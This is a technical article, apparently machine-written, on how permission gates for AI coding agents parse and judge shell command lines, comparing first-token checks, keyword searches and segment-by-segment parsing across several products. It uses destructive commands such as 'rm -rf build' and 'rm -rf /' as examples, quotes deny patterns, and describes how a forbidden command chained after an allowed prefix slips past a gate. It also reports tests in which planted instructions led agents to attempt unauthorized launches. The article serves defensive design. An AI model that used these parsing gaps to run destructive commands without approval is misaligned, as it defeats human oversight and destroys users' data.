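# Safety checks on shell commands issued by AI agents: pipelines, short-circuit operators, and matching what is judged to what runs

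## How a shell reads a command line, and what a command gate decides

An AI coding agent uses a large language model to carry out programming tasks by calling other programs. It reads and edits files, runs tests, and acts on the results. Developers have adopted these tools quickly. *From Delegation to Action Approval* (Wu, Wermke and colleagues, 2026) cites a 2025 Stack Overflow survey in which 31% of developers reported using agents, and a smaller follow-up from April 2026 in which 59% did.

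Much of an agent's work on a computer goes through a shell, the program that reads typed commands and starts other programs in response. The arrangement suits a language model. The model produces text and the shell accepts text, so a single tool that takes a command string gives the agent every program on the machine, along with the means to combine several of them in one request. OpenAI's *Rules*, part of the documentation for the company's Codex agent, shows the form such a request can take, a list of three items like this one:

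```
["bash", "-lc", "git status && npm test"]
```

The operating system starts one program here, the Bash shell. The `-c` option tells Bash to treat the third item as commands, and what runs next depends on how Bash reads that string.

A command gate is the check between the agent and the shell. For each proposed command line, it returns one of three decisions: allow (run the line without consulting anyone), ask (show it to a person and wait) or deny (refuse it). In Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, users write rules under the same three names. According to Anthropic's *Configure permissions*, Claude Code checks deny rules first, then ask, then allow, and applies the first match. Codex names the decisions allow, prompt and forbidden and applies the strictest match, which has the same effect. Docker's *Permissions* puts allow ahead of ask, so a command that matches both kinds of rule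 would run without a prompt under Docker's order but would trigger one in Claude Code and Codex.

Claude Code enforces its permission rules outside the model. Instructions in a prompt can influence which commands the model tries, but according to Anthropic they don't change what Claude Code permits. Users can add to an allow list through individual approval prompts. A later edition of Anthropic's *Configure permissions* shows the approval prompt for `npm test`, with options that include running the command once and no longer being asked about commands that begin with `npm test` in that repository.

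### From a line of text to running programs

POSIX, the standard for Unix-like systems, defines a shell language, and Bash, the GNU Project's shell, extends it. The Open Group (2024), which publishes the standard jointly with the IEEE, and GNU's *3.1.1 Shell Operation* list the same seven steps in the same order. A small line shows most of them at work:

```
ls "$HOME"/*.txt > list.txt
```

After reading the text, the shell splits it into words and operators, called tokens, by going through it one character at a time. An unquoted space ends a word, and so does an unquoted character that can begin an operator. This is why `git status&&npm test` means the same with or without spaces around `&&`. The shell adds each following character to the operator if the result is still an operator, so it reads `&&` as one operator and not two `&` signs.

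Quoting switches these rules off. A backslash protects the next character, single quotes protect everything between them, and double quotes protect everything except the dollar sign, the backquote and, in some positions, the backslash. So `echo "a && b"` is one command with one argument, while `echo a && b` is two commands. The quote marks stay in the token at this stage. In the small line, the tokens are `ls`, `"$HOME"/*.txt`, `>` and `list.txt`.

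Next the shell parses the tokens into commands and works out how the operators join them, before it expands any words. In the POSIX order, it first replaces `~`, variables, command substitutions and arithmetic, from left to right. It then splits the unquoted results into words, usually at blanks, replaces wildcards with the names of matching files, and finally removes the quote marks. Bash also expands braces, which it does before the other expansions, according to GNU's *3.5 Shell Expansions*.

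Because the shell identifies operators before it expands words, expansion cannot add an operator to the line. Aliases are an exception, since the shell replaces them with their text while it is still reading tokens. If the variable `x` holds the text `a && b`, then `echo $x` prints that text and starts nothing else. Someone checking the line in advance cannot always tell what its words will become, however. A variable can supply the name of the program, and a wildcard can turn one word into hundreds, depending on which files are in the directory. Command substitution, written `$(...)`, runs the commands inside the parentheses to obtain their output, so programs can start while the shell is still preparing the outer command.

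The shell processes redirections after expansion. For `> list.txt`, it opens the file, creating it if it does not exist and normally emptying it if it does. It also removes the operator and file name from the argument list, so `ls` never receives them. A command line can therefore overwrite a file even if the program it runs only reads.

Finally, the shell finds the program and starts it. If the name contains no slash, the shell checks its built-in commands and functions and then searches the directories in `PATH`. If the home directory contains two text files, `ls` might start with the arguments `/home/ana/notes.txt` and `/home/ana/todo.txt`, neither of which appears in the original line. The shell then normally waits for the program to end and collects its exit status.

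The shell parses the whole line before it runs any of it, but then expands and executes the commands one at a time. The Open Group specifies that in a chain of commands joined by `&&`, the shell expands a command only if it is going to execute it. A gate that reads the line beforehand can judge its text and grammar, but an earlier command may still change the variables and files that a later one depends on.

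### Simple commands, pipelines and exit status

A simple command is one program name with its arguments, variable assignments and redirections, and no operator joining it to another command. According to GNU's *3.2.2 Simple Commands*, the first word generally names the program and the rest are its arguments.

Every command returns an exit status from 0 to 255 when it ends. Zero means success and anything else means failure. GNU's *3.7.5 Exit Status* explains that a command needs only one value to report success but many to distinguish the ways it can fail. Bash returns 127 when it cannot find a command, 126 when it finds the file but cannot execute it, and 128 plus the signal number when a signal kills the program.

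A pipeline is a series of commands joined by `|`. The commands run at the same time, and each feeds its output to the next. Bash runs each one in its own subshell, a separate process, according to GNU's *3.2.3 Pipelines*.

By default, a pipeline's exit status is that of its last command. In `npm test | tee test.log`, `npm test` runs a project's tests and `tee` copies its input to both a file and its own output. If the tests fail with status 1 but `tee` succeeds, the pipeline returns 0, and the shell treats it as a success when running the rest of the line.

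With the `pipefail` option on, a pipeline instead returns the status of the rightmost command that failed, or 0 if none did, so the same run returns 1. The shell uses the setting in force when the pipeline starts. In *Add set -o pipefail*, Weeks traces the option to the shell ksh93 in 1998 and argues that POSIX should include it because most pipelines in scripts rely on every command succeeding. The 2024 edition of the standard includes it. Someone still has to turn it on, and the text of a pipeline doesn't show whether anyone has.

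### How the operators group

With the short-circuit operators `&&` and `||`, the shell runs the next command only under a condition. What came before must have succeeded for `&&` and failed for `||`. A semicolon makes the shell wait for what precedes it to finish, then run the next command whatever the result. A single `&` makes the shell run what precedes it in the background and continue without waiting.

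When a line contains several operators, `|` binds tightest. `&&` and `||` come next, with equal precedence, and group from the left. `;` and `&` bind loosest, also with equal precedence, as GNU's *3.2.4 Lists of Commands* confirms for Bash.

The equal rank of `&&` and `||` catches out programmers, because in C and many other languages `&&` binds more tightly. The Open Group gives this example, in which `true` is a command that always succeeds:

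```
true || echo foo && echo bar
```

The shell reads `true || echo foo && echo bar` as `(true || echo foo) && echo bar`. Because `true` succeeds, the shell skips `echo foo`. The left side as a whole has then succeeded, so the shell runs `echo bar` and the line prints `bar`. Under C's precedence rule, the line would mean `true || (echo foo && echo bar)` and print nothing.

### The example line and its policy

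The following line is short and of a kind that an agent might well write while working on a JavaScript project:

```
git status && npm test | tee test.log || rm -rf build
```

`git status` reports which files in a repository have changed. `npm test` runs the project's tests, `tee test.log` saves a copy of their output, and `rm -rf build` deletes the `build` directory and its contents without asking for confirmation. Someone who writes a line combining these commands presumably wants to delete a bad build when the tests fail.

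The pipe binds first, so `npm test | tee test.log` forms a unit. Grouping from the left then joins `git status` to that unit, and the `||` applies to the result of both:

```
(git status AND (npm test | tee test.log)) OR rm -rf build

OR
├── AND
│   ├── git status
│   └── pipeline
│       ├── npm test
│       └── tee test.log
└── rm -rf build
```

Whether `rm` runs depends on the exit statuses of the commands to its left. The line has no variables, wildcards or redirections, so a gate first has to parse its structure correctly.

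The policy for this line allows `git status`, `npm test` and `tee`, and requires a prompt for everything else. It has no deny rules and does not limit which files `tee` may write. Real users end up with similar policies. Docker's documentation lists `git status` as a safe command, Claude Code runs read-only forms of `git` without a prompt, and a developer tired of approving `npm test` can save a rule for it. Under this policy, a gate should ask about the example line because `rm -rf build` is not on the allow list.

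### False allows and false alarms

A gate can make two kinds of error. A false allow lets through a command whose effects break the policy. A false alarm blocks a permitted command or sends it to a person. Reducing one tends to increase the other, and Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* gives figures for this tradeoff. Auto mode is a gate in which a language model classifier replaces the human approver.

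Its first stage is a quick filter instructed to err toward blocking. On its own, that stage wrongly flagged 8.5% of harmless actions in a sample of 10,000 tool calls by Anthropic's staff, and it missed 6.6% of 52 real actions that had gone beyond what the user wanted. Adding a second stage, which reasons about whatever the first has flagged, cut the false alarms to 0.4% but raised the misses to 17%. Both miss rates are rough estimates because they come from only 52 actions. The miss rate also rose, from 1.8% to 5.7%, on 1,000 synthetic attempts to leak data.

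A false allow lets a harmful command run. A false alarm does less immediate harm, since the person can press a key and carry on, but pressing the key becomes a habit. Anthropic reported that users accept 93% of Claude Code's permission prompts, and Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) put the figure at 97%. The rate alone is weak evidence of this habit, because most prompts probably concern harmless commands, as the company acknowledges.

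An experiment in the same article is better evidence. A research vendor gave 1,053 paid testers a coding task and, partway through each session, replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Of the testers, 143 (13.6%) refused it. They caught about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session, but about 5% after 50 or more prompts. The low overall rate may not apply to people guarding their own files, since the testers worked in a test environment with nothing of their own at stake. Anthropic also published the result in support of replacing prompts with its classifier. The decline over a session is more relevant to false alarms, because each false alarm adds a prompt.

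In a survey of 203 users of coding agents by Wu and colleagues, 64% said they often approved at least one of seven types of action without close review. The share was 61% among those who carefully reviewed most or all of the code their agents wrote and 67% among the rest, a difference that chance could easily explain. Among respondents aware of a security or privacy problem involving agents, 70% often approved something without close review, compared with 43% of those who reported no such awareness. Heavier users may both hear of more incidents and approve more actions, but the association held after the researchers adjusted for how often and how long people had used agents. The respondents came through LinkedIn, personal referrals and a paid panel, so the percentages can't be assumed to hold for developers in general.

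Some people stop answering prompts altogether. Anthropic found that 25% of interactive Claude Code sessions start in the mode that bypasses them.

How well an ask protects the user therefore depends on how much attention the user gives it. Suppose an agent proposes 100 dangerous commands and the testers' figures are accurate. If a gate asks about all 100, but also asks about so many other commands that its user catches only 5% of the dangerous ones, five are stopped. If a gate wrongly allows ten and asks about the other 90, but prompts rarely enough that its user catches 17% of those, about 15 are stopped. The real rates will vary from person to person, and a deny doesn't depend on anyone's attention, but a gate with more false allows can still be safer.

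A gate could prevent a false allow on the example line by requiring approval for every line that contains an operator. But it would then also require approval each time the agent wrote `git status && npm test`, which the policy permits, and whoever saw the prompt for `rm -rf build` would already have approved dozens that looked much like it.

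## Judging a command by its first word

A first-token check judges a whole command line only by its first word. In its simplest form, the check takes the text before the first blank and looks it up in an allow list. If the word is on the list, the entire line goes to the shell. Otherwise, the line needs approval before it can run.

The first word of a command is often too coarse a basis for judging it. In *Support sub-command allow/deny list (e.g. `git status`)*, a user of the Cursor code editor describes keeping `git` off the allow list for fear that the agent would delete a branch, and asks for a way to allow the harmless `git status`. Most products therefore let a rule cover several opening words, such as `git status`.

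Products differ in how they compare the start of a command. Some compare characters, so a rule for `ls` also covers `lsof`, a different program. In Claude Code, according to Anthropic, the rule `ls*` matches `lsof`, but `ls *`, with a space, does not. According to JetBrains' *Add commands to Action Allowlist*, the company's Junie agent matches prefixes by whole words, so `git` covers `git push` but not the separate program `git-annex`. Other gates use regular expressions, text patterns in which `^` marks the start of the text. The pattern `^git\b` requires a word boundary after `git`, but a hyphen creates one, so the pattern also matches `git-annex`.

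A keyword search instead scans the whole line for alarming text such as `rm` or `sudo`, and a match leads to a request for approval or a denial. Zed's *Tool Permissions*, the documentation for another code editor with a built-in agent, gives the pattern `\brm\b`, which matches "rm" but not "storm".

Many gates use both methods. *Building Effective AI Coding Agents for the Terminal* (Bui, 2026) describes OpenDev, an open-source agent with four types of rule. One compares the command with an exact text, one with a prefix, and one with a regular expression, while the fourth denies any command that contains a dangerous pattern. Zed's sample rules tie most allow patterns to the start of the text and let deny patterns match anywhere. *Anatomy of an Agent Harness* (Joshi, 2026) gives a reason for treating allow and deny rules differently: approving a command requires reading it exactly, whereas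 refusing requires catching anything that might be dangerous.

### Why designers chose it

The program's name is usually the most informative word in a simple command. `ls` lists files and `rm` deletes them, whatever the arguments. A check that uses only this word needs no shell parser and takes almost no time. Its rules are short enough for a user to read and write without training.

Prefixes also suit the way people grant approvals. Joshi compares three things a gate could save when a user chooses "always allow". Saving the exact command is safest, but the user then has to approve every small variation. Saving a whole tool allows anything the tool can do. A prefix falls between them. An agent fixing a login page might run `npm test`, then `npm test -- login`, then `npm test -- login --verbose`, and a user who has approved the first is unlikely to want a prompt for the others. This is why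 Claude Code's prompt for `npm test` offers to save a prefix.

Prefix rules remain common. *ParseGap* (Li, 2026), a study of eight coding agents in November 2026, lists them in Roo Code, Mistral Vibe and Codex, but all three parse the line into commands before they apply the rules. A prefix can reasonably describe one command, but it causes problems when a gate applies it to a line that contains several.

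### The example line

Under the example policy, a first-token check allows any line that begins with `git status`, `npm test` or `tee`. The example line was:

```
git status && npm test | tee test.log || rm -rf build
```

The command line begins with `git status`, so the check allows it. The check bases this verdict on two of the line's nine words, not counting operators. The shell then receives all four commands, and if the earlier exit statuses cause `rm -rf build` to run, the shell deletes the directory without a prompt. This is a false allow, and the check would have allowed the line whatever came after `git status`.

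The hidden premise is that the first word stands for the whole line. Suppose a line contains the simple commands *c*₁, *c*₂, …, *c*ₙ. The policy permits the line only if it permits every one of them, but the check tests only *c*₁. With one command, the two tests coincide. With more, the verdict can depend on the order:

```
rm -rf build; git status
git status; rm -rf build
```

Both lines delete the directory and report on the repository. A first-token check asks about the first line and allows the second.

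On Cursor's forum, kev_rm asked what would stop an agent with permission to run `grep -r` from adding a harmful command after a semicolon or a pipe. The reply was that Cursor also checks commands that follow, for example, a pipe, and asks for permission if the second command is not on the list of allowed commands.

The premise can also fail without an operator. A command substitution, as in `git status $(...)`, runs other commands first. Some programs also run other programs. For example, `timeout 30 npm test` starts `timeout`, which runs the tests and stops them after 30 seconds. Allowing `timeout` as a first word therefore allows every command that can follow it. Claude Code removes `timeout` and a few similar wrappers before comparing a command with its rules, so that the rule for `npm test` applies.

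### Harmless lines it stops

The first word can also be less trustworthy than the rest of the line, or have no effect at all. Language models often put a comment above a command:

```
# run the tests
npm test
```

The shell ignores the comment and runs `npm test`, which the policy permits. A first-token check finds `#`, which isn't on any allow list, and prompts the user for approval. A variable assignment causes the same problem. In `NODE_ENV=test npm test`, the first word sets a variable for that command, and the program's name comes second. When Claude Code looks for a matching allow rule, it skips assignments to certain variables that Anthropic considers safe. For deny rules it skips any assignment, which is consistent with Joshi's point about approving and refusing.

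Lines that begin with `cd`, the command that changes the working directory, are harder to deal with. Consider these two:

```
cd web && npm test
cd web && rm -rf build
```

The check treats the test run and the deletion the same way whether or not `cd` is on the list. If `cd` is not on the list, the check prompts the user about both. The example policy requires this because it names only three commands, but a user who regards changing directory as harmless would call the first prompt a false alarm. If the user adds `cd` to the list, the check allows both.

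In *Serious permissions model for auto-run commands*, a Cursor user describes how their agent had learned to begin work on a project with `cd tofu`, followed by a command that changes cloud infrastructure without asking for confirmation. The user feared that allowing the seemingly harmless `cd` would also allow the second command.

Some prompts on such lines are deliberate. Claude Code prompts the user when a line changes directory and then runs `git`, even if it would allow each command alone, because `git` can execute scripts in the new directory.

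Keyword searches produce false alarms because they treat data as if it were a command. `grep -rn "rm -rf" scripts/` only searches a folder for text and deletes nothing, but a keyword search for `rm -rf` would flag it. An agent whose command was blocked can trigger the same rule again by quoting the command in a note. dicklesworthstone's *destructive command guard*, the description of a tool that screens agents' commands, lists as a feature that the tool blocks `rm -rf /` but not a `grep` for "rm -rf".

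Ignoring everything inside quotation marks would not solve this, because quoted text can be a command, as in `bash -c "rm -rf build"`. To tell quoted commands from other quoted text, a gate must account for which program receives the text and what that program does with it.

Operators inside quotation marks may also cause false alarms. In *How does command allowlist/denylist really work?*, a Cursor user reports getting approval prompts for `grep` even though it is on the allow list. The search term in the user's example contains a quoted `|`. A check that treated every `|` as a pipe would produce these prompts, though the report does not establish the cause.

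The following table compares both methods on seven lines under the example policy. The keyword search asks about any line that contains the word `rm` and allows the rest. In the sixth line, `--grep "rm"` makes the test program run only tests whose names contain "rm".

| Line | Policy | First-token check | Keyword search |
|---|---|---|---|
| `npm test` | allow | allow | allow |
| `rm -rf build` | ask | ask | ask |
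| `git status && npm test` | allow | allow | allow |
| The example line | ask | allow (false allow) | ask |
| `npm test` piped into `python3 report.py` | ask | allow (false allow) | allow (false allow) |
| `npm test -- --grep "rm"` | allow | allow | ask (false alarm) |
| `# run the tests`, with `npm test` on the next line | allow | ask (false alarm) | allow |

A gate could run both checks and apply the stricter verdict. It would ask about the example line but still allow the pipeline into Python, because the pipeline begins with an allowed command and contains no alarming word. It would also raise both false alarms.

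### How much a list of patterns catches

*CARE* (Liu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) measured a keyword search as a baseline for a more elaborate gate. The search consisted of 22 regular expressions for high-priority destructive commands and commands that send data off the machine.

They tested it on 549 commands, 220 dangerous and 329 safe. Of the dangerous commands, 137 came from Atomic Red Team, a public library of small tests that imitate attackers' techniques, and 71 came from RedCode-Exec, a benchmark of risky code for agents. The researchers added 12 well-known attacks that these collections underrepresent. Of the safe commands, 299 came from NL2Bash, which pairs English descriptions with shell commands, and 30 were commands that developers commonly use. When they split the data, the researchers kept commands derived from the same template together so that their own gate would not be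 tuned on near-copies of the test commands.

Checking a command against the 22 patterns took about 0.01 milliseconds. The patterns caught 38 of the 220 dangerous commands (17.27%) and raised no false alarms.

The absence of false alarms is weak evidence that a check is good, because a gate that allows every command also raises none. The researchers' results include such a gate for comparison. Zero false alarms in 329 safe commands is also compatible, at 95% confidence, with a true rate of up to about 0.9%, or 90 needless stops per 10,000 safe commands.

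The same patterns did raise false alarms elsewhere. They flagged 0.40% of one further sample of safe commands and 1.63% of another, and they denied commands in 3 of 300 harmless tasks. Even these samples were fairly easy for a keyword search, because the researchers drew them from a pool of 547 commands and had filtered 377 of those to exclude text that a simple pattern would flag.

The 22 patterns caught 13 of 26 destructive commands in the main test, but only 1 of 80 that reached outside the agent's working folder and 1 of 24 that gave an attacker lasting access. These categories are approximate, but the gap is large. A keyword search works best when dangerous commands share stock phrases. On 123 snippets from published exploits, the same patterns had the highest F1 score of the 12 methods compared. F1 combines catches and false alarms into one measure. That score and the false alarm rate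 imply that the patterns caught 86 of the 123 snippets, or about 70%.

The patterns did much worse on 600 attack commands written by a language model. In an isolated container, 449 of these ran successfully without a gate, and 436 still did with the patterns in place. The patterns denied 49 commands, but 36 of those would have failed anyway.

None of these figures measures what share of attacks a first-token check would catch. The 22 patterns stop only the commands they match, while an allow list stops every command whose first word is not on it. An allow list as short as the example policy's would probably have stopped nearly all the attacks in the main test, but also nearly all the safe commands.

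### Zed's change of early 2026

Zed at first matched patterns against the whole line. Pull request 47807, a proposed change to the editor's code with screenshots from 28 January 2026, replaced this method. Feldman explains in *Fix shell injection vulnerability in terminal tool permissions* that a user could tell Zed to allow any command that matched `^ls`. Because the pattern covered only the start of the line, an attacker could add a destructive command after an operator and Zed would approve both commands.

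Zed now parses the line into its individual commands and compares each with the user's patterns. It approves the line automatically only if every command matches an allow pattern. Users could keep their existing rules, since `^ls` now refers to the start of a command, not the line. If the user had rules for `git status`, `npm test` and `tee`, `rm -rf build` in the example line would match none of them, and Zed would ask for approval under its default setting.

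The flaw may have affected few people, because Zed still kept these detailed permissions behind a feature flag, a switch that hides unfinished features from most users. The pull request does not report any attack that exploited the flaw.

The repair took far more code than the original check. Before the change, Zed built its suggested patterns by taking the text up to the first whitespace. The pull request added a third-party shell parser and a 396-line module to extract commands from the parser's output. In all, it added 1,082 lines, including tests. The parser could not handle Nushell, Elvish or rc, which join commands in other ways, so Zed at first refused to apply allow patterns in those shells. Zed's documentation now lists all three as supported.

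Zed still searches the raw text of the line to enforce a few built-in rules against deleting critical directories, such as the home directory. It also applies these rules to each command that the parser finds in the line, and no setting can turn them off.

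## Judging every segment of the line

A segment-by-segment check splits a command line at its operators, judges each piece, and combines the verdicts into one. Zed's early 2026 change worked this way. GitHub's *Bash Command Parser Specification* describes the procedure in more detail than most products do. The July 2026 version, still a draft, covers the parser behind the permission checks in the Copilot SDK, a toolkit based on GitHub's coding assistant. GitHub wrote the specification by documenting a parser already in use.

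### From a line to a list of commands

The parser reads the line one character at a time and keeps track of whether it is at the top level, inside single quotes, inside double quotes or inside a command substitution, `$(...)`. It counts nested parentheses to find the one that closes the outermost substitution. It cuts the line only at the top level, wherever it finds `&&`, `||`, `|`, `;` or a line break. It doesn't cut at a line break that comes right after a backslash, because the command continues on the next line.

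```
NODE_ENV=test npm test && echo "passed; see log"
```

In `NODE_ENV=test npm test && echo "passed; see log"`, the parser splits at `&&`, which is at the top level, but not at the semicolon, which is inside double quotes. This gives two segments, `NODE_ENV=test npm test` and `echo "passed; see log"`. A check that looked for operators without tracking quotes would also split at the semicolon and produce three segments, the last beginning with `see`.

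Next, the parser finds the command name in each segment. It strips leading variable assignments and skips `!`, which reverses an exit status, as well as braces and words such as `then` and `do`, which come before a command in a conditional or loop. The first word left is the name, so this line yields `npm` and `echo`. Segments without a command, such as the `fi` that closes a conditional, yield no name. The parser returns the names in order, without repeats.

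Command names alone are not enough to apply the example policy, which permits `git status` but not every `git` command. A gate with rules like this also has to check each segment's arguments, as Claude Code, Codex and Zed do.

GitHub requires at least 15 tests of the parser, plus others that change a line in ways that shouldn't affect the result. Adding spaces around an operator, or an assignment before a command, must not change the names. Moving an operator inside quotation marks must leave a single segment. GitHub also recommends running the same inputs through every implementation and comparing the results. These tests can show that a parser is inconsistent, but they don't compare it with Bash, which determines what runs.

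### Combining the verdicts

Once every segment has a verdict, the strictest one applies to the whole line. If allow ranks lowest, then ask, then deny, the rule for segments *s*₁ to *s*ₙ is:

```
verdict(line) = strictest of verdict(s1), verdict(s2), ..., verdict(sn)
```

The gate therefore allows a line only if the policy permits the command in every segment, so one forbidden command stops the whole line. The gate cannot drop that command and run the rest, because later commands may depend on its exit status or output, and the shorter line could then do something the agent never proposed.

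The gate needs a separate rule for lines in which its parser finds no segments. "Every segment passes" is true of an empty list, and Python's `all` function, for example, returns true for one. A gate that only checks whether every segment passes would therefore allow such a line. GitHub requires the gate to deny it unless the user has a rule for exactly that text. A cautious gate would also ask the user whenever a single segment yields no command name and the gate can't determine why.

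GitHub also warns that the parser's output does not prove that a line is safe. The parser identifies the commands, but the gate must still check each one against the rules, even when the line contains a single command.

Under the example policy, the procedure gives these verdicts:

| Segment of the example line | Name | Verdict |
|---|---|---|
| `git status` | `git` | allow |
| `npm test` | `npm` | allow |
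| `tee test.log` | `tee` | allow |
| `rm -rf build` | `rm` | ask |
| Whole line | | ask |

An `rm` anywhere in the line now sends the line to a person, even if the earlier commands are about to succeed and the shell would therefore skip the deletion.

The same procedure gives the right answer on at least six of the seven lines used to compare first-token checks with keyword searches. It prompts for approval of the pipeline into Python, which both of those methods allowed. The remaining line has a comment above `npm test`. GitHub's published rules don't mention comments, so a gate that followed them literally would treat `#` as a command name and raise a false alarm. A parser that recognizes comments avoids this.

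### Commands inside other commands

Keeping `$(...)` in one piece stops the parser from splitting the outer command, but the commands inside the parentheses also run. Many gates therefore repeat the whole procedure on that text and add the results to the list. For `echo "$(git status)"`, they judge both `echo` and `git status`. Inside single quotes, the shell treats the substitution as plain text, so PraisonAI, a framework for building agents, extracts nothing from it.

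Zed's parser turns the line into a tree. Feldman's code walks through the tree's substitutions, loops, function bodies and conditionals, and collects the commands from every branch, regardless of which will run.

Programs that start other programs need a different kind of recursion, usually called unwrapping. Consider this line:

```
timeout 30 bash -c "npm test && rm -rf build"
```

The `&&` is inside quotation marks, so the line has one segment, and its command name is `timeout`. A gate with a rule for `timeout` removes the name and the time limit and finds `bash -c`. Bash will read the next argument as a command line, so the gate removes the quotation marks and checks `npm test && rm -rf build` as a new line. That line has two segments, and the second, `rm -rf build`, is not on the allow list, so the gate requests approval.

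To unwrap a program, the gate needs a list of that program's options and which of them take values. In `timeout -k 5 30 npm test`, the `5` belongs to `-k`. A gate without this information would read `5` as the time limit and `30` as the name of the inner program. With `env`, variable assignments can come before the inner program. `sudo` runs the inner command with an administrator's rights, so a ban on `rm` should still apply after `sudo`, but permission to run `npm test` doesn't imply permission to run it as administrator.

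For a fixed list of wrapper programs, including `timeout`, `nice` and `nohup`, Claude Code judges the command inside, according to Anthropic. It does the same for `xargs`, which builds commands from its input, but only when `xargs` has no options of its own. A prefix rule can't approve `watch` or `flock`, which also run other commands, so Claude Code asks the user for approval in the ordinary manual mode. Development tools such as `npx` and `docker exec` are not on the list, and a broad rule for one of them covers whatever command follows. Anthropic advises users to write rules that name both the tool and the inner command. With runok, a gate that users can add to Claude Code, users can instead declare wrappers themselves, with entries such as `sudo <cmd>`.

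*A Deterministic Security Runtime for LLM Agents* (Metere, 2026) takes recursion further. Its gate protects high-performance computing systems, where a single command can commit thousands of machine-hours. The gate judges only commands that launch or control computing jobs, and it allows or refuses each one, with no option to ask. It splits the line into simple commands, unwraps `env`, `timeout` and similar programs, and examines the quoted text passed to `sh -c`. It also reads the commands in script files, so if an agent submits a batch script, the gate finds any further launches inside it.

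This recursion stops at a fixed depth, and the gate rejects anything deeper. It also rejects a launch with an unclosed quotation mark, an unrecognized option, or a variable in the launcher's arguments that it can't resolve.

Metere tested the gate with 16 agents running on a real model. Instructions planted by the experimenter led the agents to attempt 24 launches, and the gate denied all of them while allowing all 108 legitimate ones. With zero misses in 24 attempts, the true miss rate could still be as high as about 12%, at 95% confidence. This estimate assumes the attempts were independent, which they may not have been.

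Some designers use a language model to split the line into commands. In *Sema Code* (2026), the model also looks for known attack patterns, and the start of each command must match an allow list. Metere rejects using a second model to judge the first, for two reasons that also apply to splitting. An auditor should be able to reproduce every verdict from the policy and the command text, and an attacker who has manipulated an agent into issuing a command should not be able to get the gate to allow it in the same way.

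### What the products split, and what they do when they can't

A gate's designers can list the syntax they consider unsafe and have the gate split everything else, or list the syntax they understand and have it split only that. Joshi points out that when a command uses a construct nobody thought of, the first kind of gate lets it through by default, while the second prompts for approval.

Codex follows the second approach. According to OpenAI, Codex splits a line only if it consists of plain words joined by `&&`, `||`, `;` or `|`. The example line qualifies, so Codex judges its four commands separately. If a line contains a redirection, a variable, a wildcard, a substitution or a loop, Codex treats the whole line as one unit, the argument to `bash -lc`. Li found the same operators and the same restriction in the November 2026 version.

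A small change to a line shows how much this matters:

```
git status && npm test > test.log
```

Because this line contains a `>`, Codex doesn't split it, so the user's rules for `git status` and `npm test` can't approve it. Claude Code splits it, then checks `test.log` against its rules for files, as if the agent had written the file directly. PraisonAI adds an item to the list, `write:test.log`, so a user can forbid writing to a directory without forbidding the program whose output goes there.

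Claude Code splits a command line at `&&`, `||`, `;`, `|`, `|&`, `&` and line breaks. The line runs without a prompt only if each command is allowed by a rule or recognized as read-only. Deny and ask rules also apply to commands inside substitutions, subshells and loop bodies. Claude Code treats an unfinished line such as `npm test &&` as unparseable and doesn't split it to look for matching allow rules, so a rule for `npm` doesn't approve it. In manual mode, Claude Code always prompts for lines of more than 10,000 characters.

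The gates differ most in what they do with a line that they can't parse:

| Gate | Commands nested inside others | Line it cannot parse |
|---|---|---|
| Codex | Treats the whole line as one unit | Treats the whole line as one unit |
| Claude Code | Applies deny and ask rules to them | Asks |
| Zed | Adds them to the list | Ignores all allow patterns |
| PraisonAI | Adds them to the list | Judges the whole line as one command, with its older matcher |
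| Metere's gate | Follows quoted commands and scripts to a fixed depth | Refuses |

PraisonAI chose its fallback so that no existing rule would become weaker. This makes sense for deny rules, which still catch everything they caught before. It is riskier for allow rules, because a broad one can still approve a line that the gate couldn't parse. Zed's fallback avoids this by disabling only the patterns that could approve the line.

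Joshi explains why the two kinds of rule need different fallbacks. He describes a gate that reads each line in two ways, strictly when approving and permissively when refusing. Under the strict reading, the gate lets a command run without asking only if it parses every character exactly as every supported shell would. Joshi reports that his own program doesn't yet meet this standard.

The products also have to decide what to save when a user approves a chain and asks not to see the prompt again. Claude Code saves a separate rule for each command that needed approval, up to five for one line. If a user approves `git status && npm test` this way, Claude Code saves a rule for `npm test`, which applies no matter what comes before that command. This avoids a new prompt for every new combination. However, a user might accept `rm -rf build` in the example line because it follows a failure, and the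 saved rule would let it run after a success too.

### The cost in false alarms

A line is allowed only if every segment passes, so long lines cause more prompts than short ones. Suppose a user's rules cover 95% of the harmless commands that an agent writes, so that a single harmless command causes a prompt 5% of the time. If the commands in a line are independent, a line of four harmless commands causes a prompt about 19% of the time, since 0.95⁴ is about 0.81. Real commands are not independent, but longer lines still cause more prompts.

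Li measured both kinds of error on ordinary commands. The policy allowed a short list of programs and subcommands for inspecting files and repositories. Of the commands in the test, 161 were read-only and eligible under this policy, and 316 were not read-only, so the policy did not permit them. The results for six of the agents were:

| Agent | Harmless commands stopped, of 161 | Other commands allowed, of 316 |
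|---|---|---|
| Codex | 37 (23.0%) | 2 |
| Mistral Vibe | 28 (17.4%) | 2 |
| Continue | 18 (11.2%) | 18 |
| Gemini CLI | 6 (3.7%) | 39 |
| Roo Code | 4 (2.5%) | 12 |
| OpenCode | 4 (2.5%) | 48 |

Codex stopped nearly a quarter of the harmless commands, which is consistent with its not splitting anything beyond plain words, although the totals don't separate that cause from others. It also made only two false allows. A tool doesn't always have to stop more harmless commands to make fewer false allows, since Roo Code did at least as well as Gemini CLI and OpenCode on both measures. But when Li tested commands written as attacks, Roo Code allowed a far larger share than either of them.

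In February 2026, Codex developer Dylan Hurd wrote in a commit message preserved in *Agent IDE*, a modified copy of Codex, that the model `gpt-5.3-codex` tended to write complicated shell scripts and then suggest that the user save a rule covering only part of the script. A user who saved that rule would have seen the same prompt the next time. Hurd's change hides a suggested rule unless the rule would approve the whole displayed command.

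Other false alarms come from extra checks that a gate adds to the splitting. The runok documentation, in a copy from April 2026, shows Claude Code prompting for this line despite the user's allow rules:

```
git log --oneline -5 && echo "---" && git status
```

The on-screen reason was that the command contained quoted characters in flag names, but the quoted dashes were only text for `echo` to print. Anthropic has since relaxed at least one such check. In May 2026, by Anthropic's account, any line that combined `cd` with `git` triggered a permission prompt. By October, combining `git` with a `cd` to the agent's current directory no longer did.

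*Stop asking me* (2026) describes a production release during which Claude Code asked a developer for the fourteenth time whether it could run `gcloud logging read`, which reads logs from Google's cloud service. He had already approved the command several times in that session. He had tried to cover his work with more than 80 narrow patterns and spent a week adjusting their colons, spaces and wildcards. Prompts still appeared for lines that changed into a repository, fetched new commits with `git` and listed the first few.

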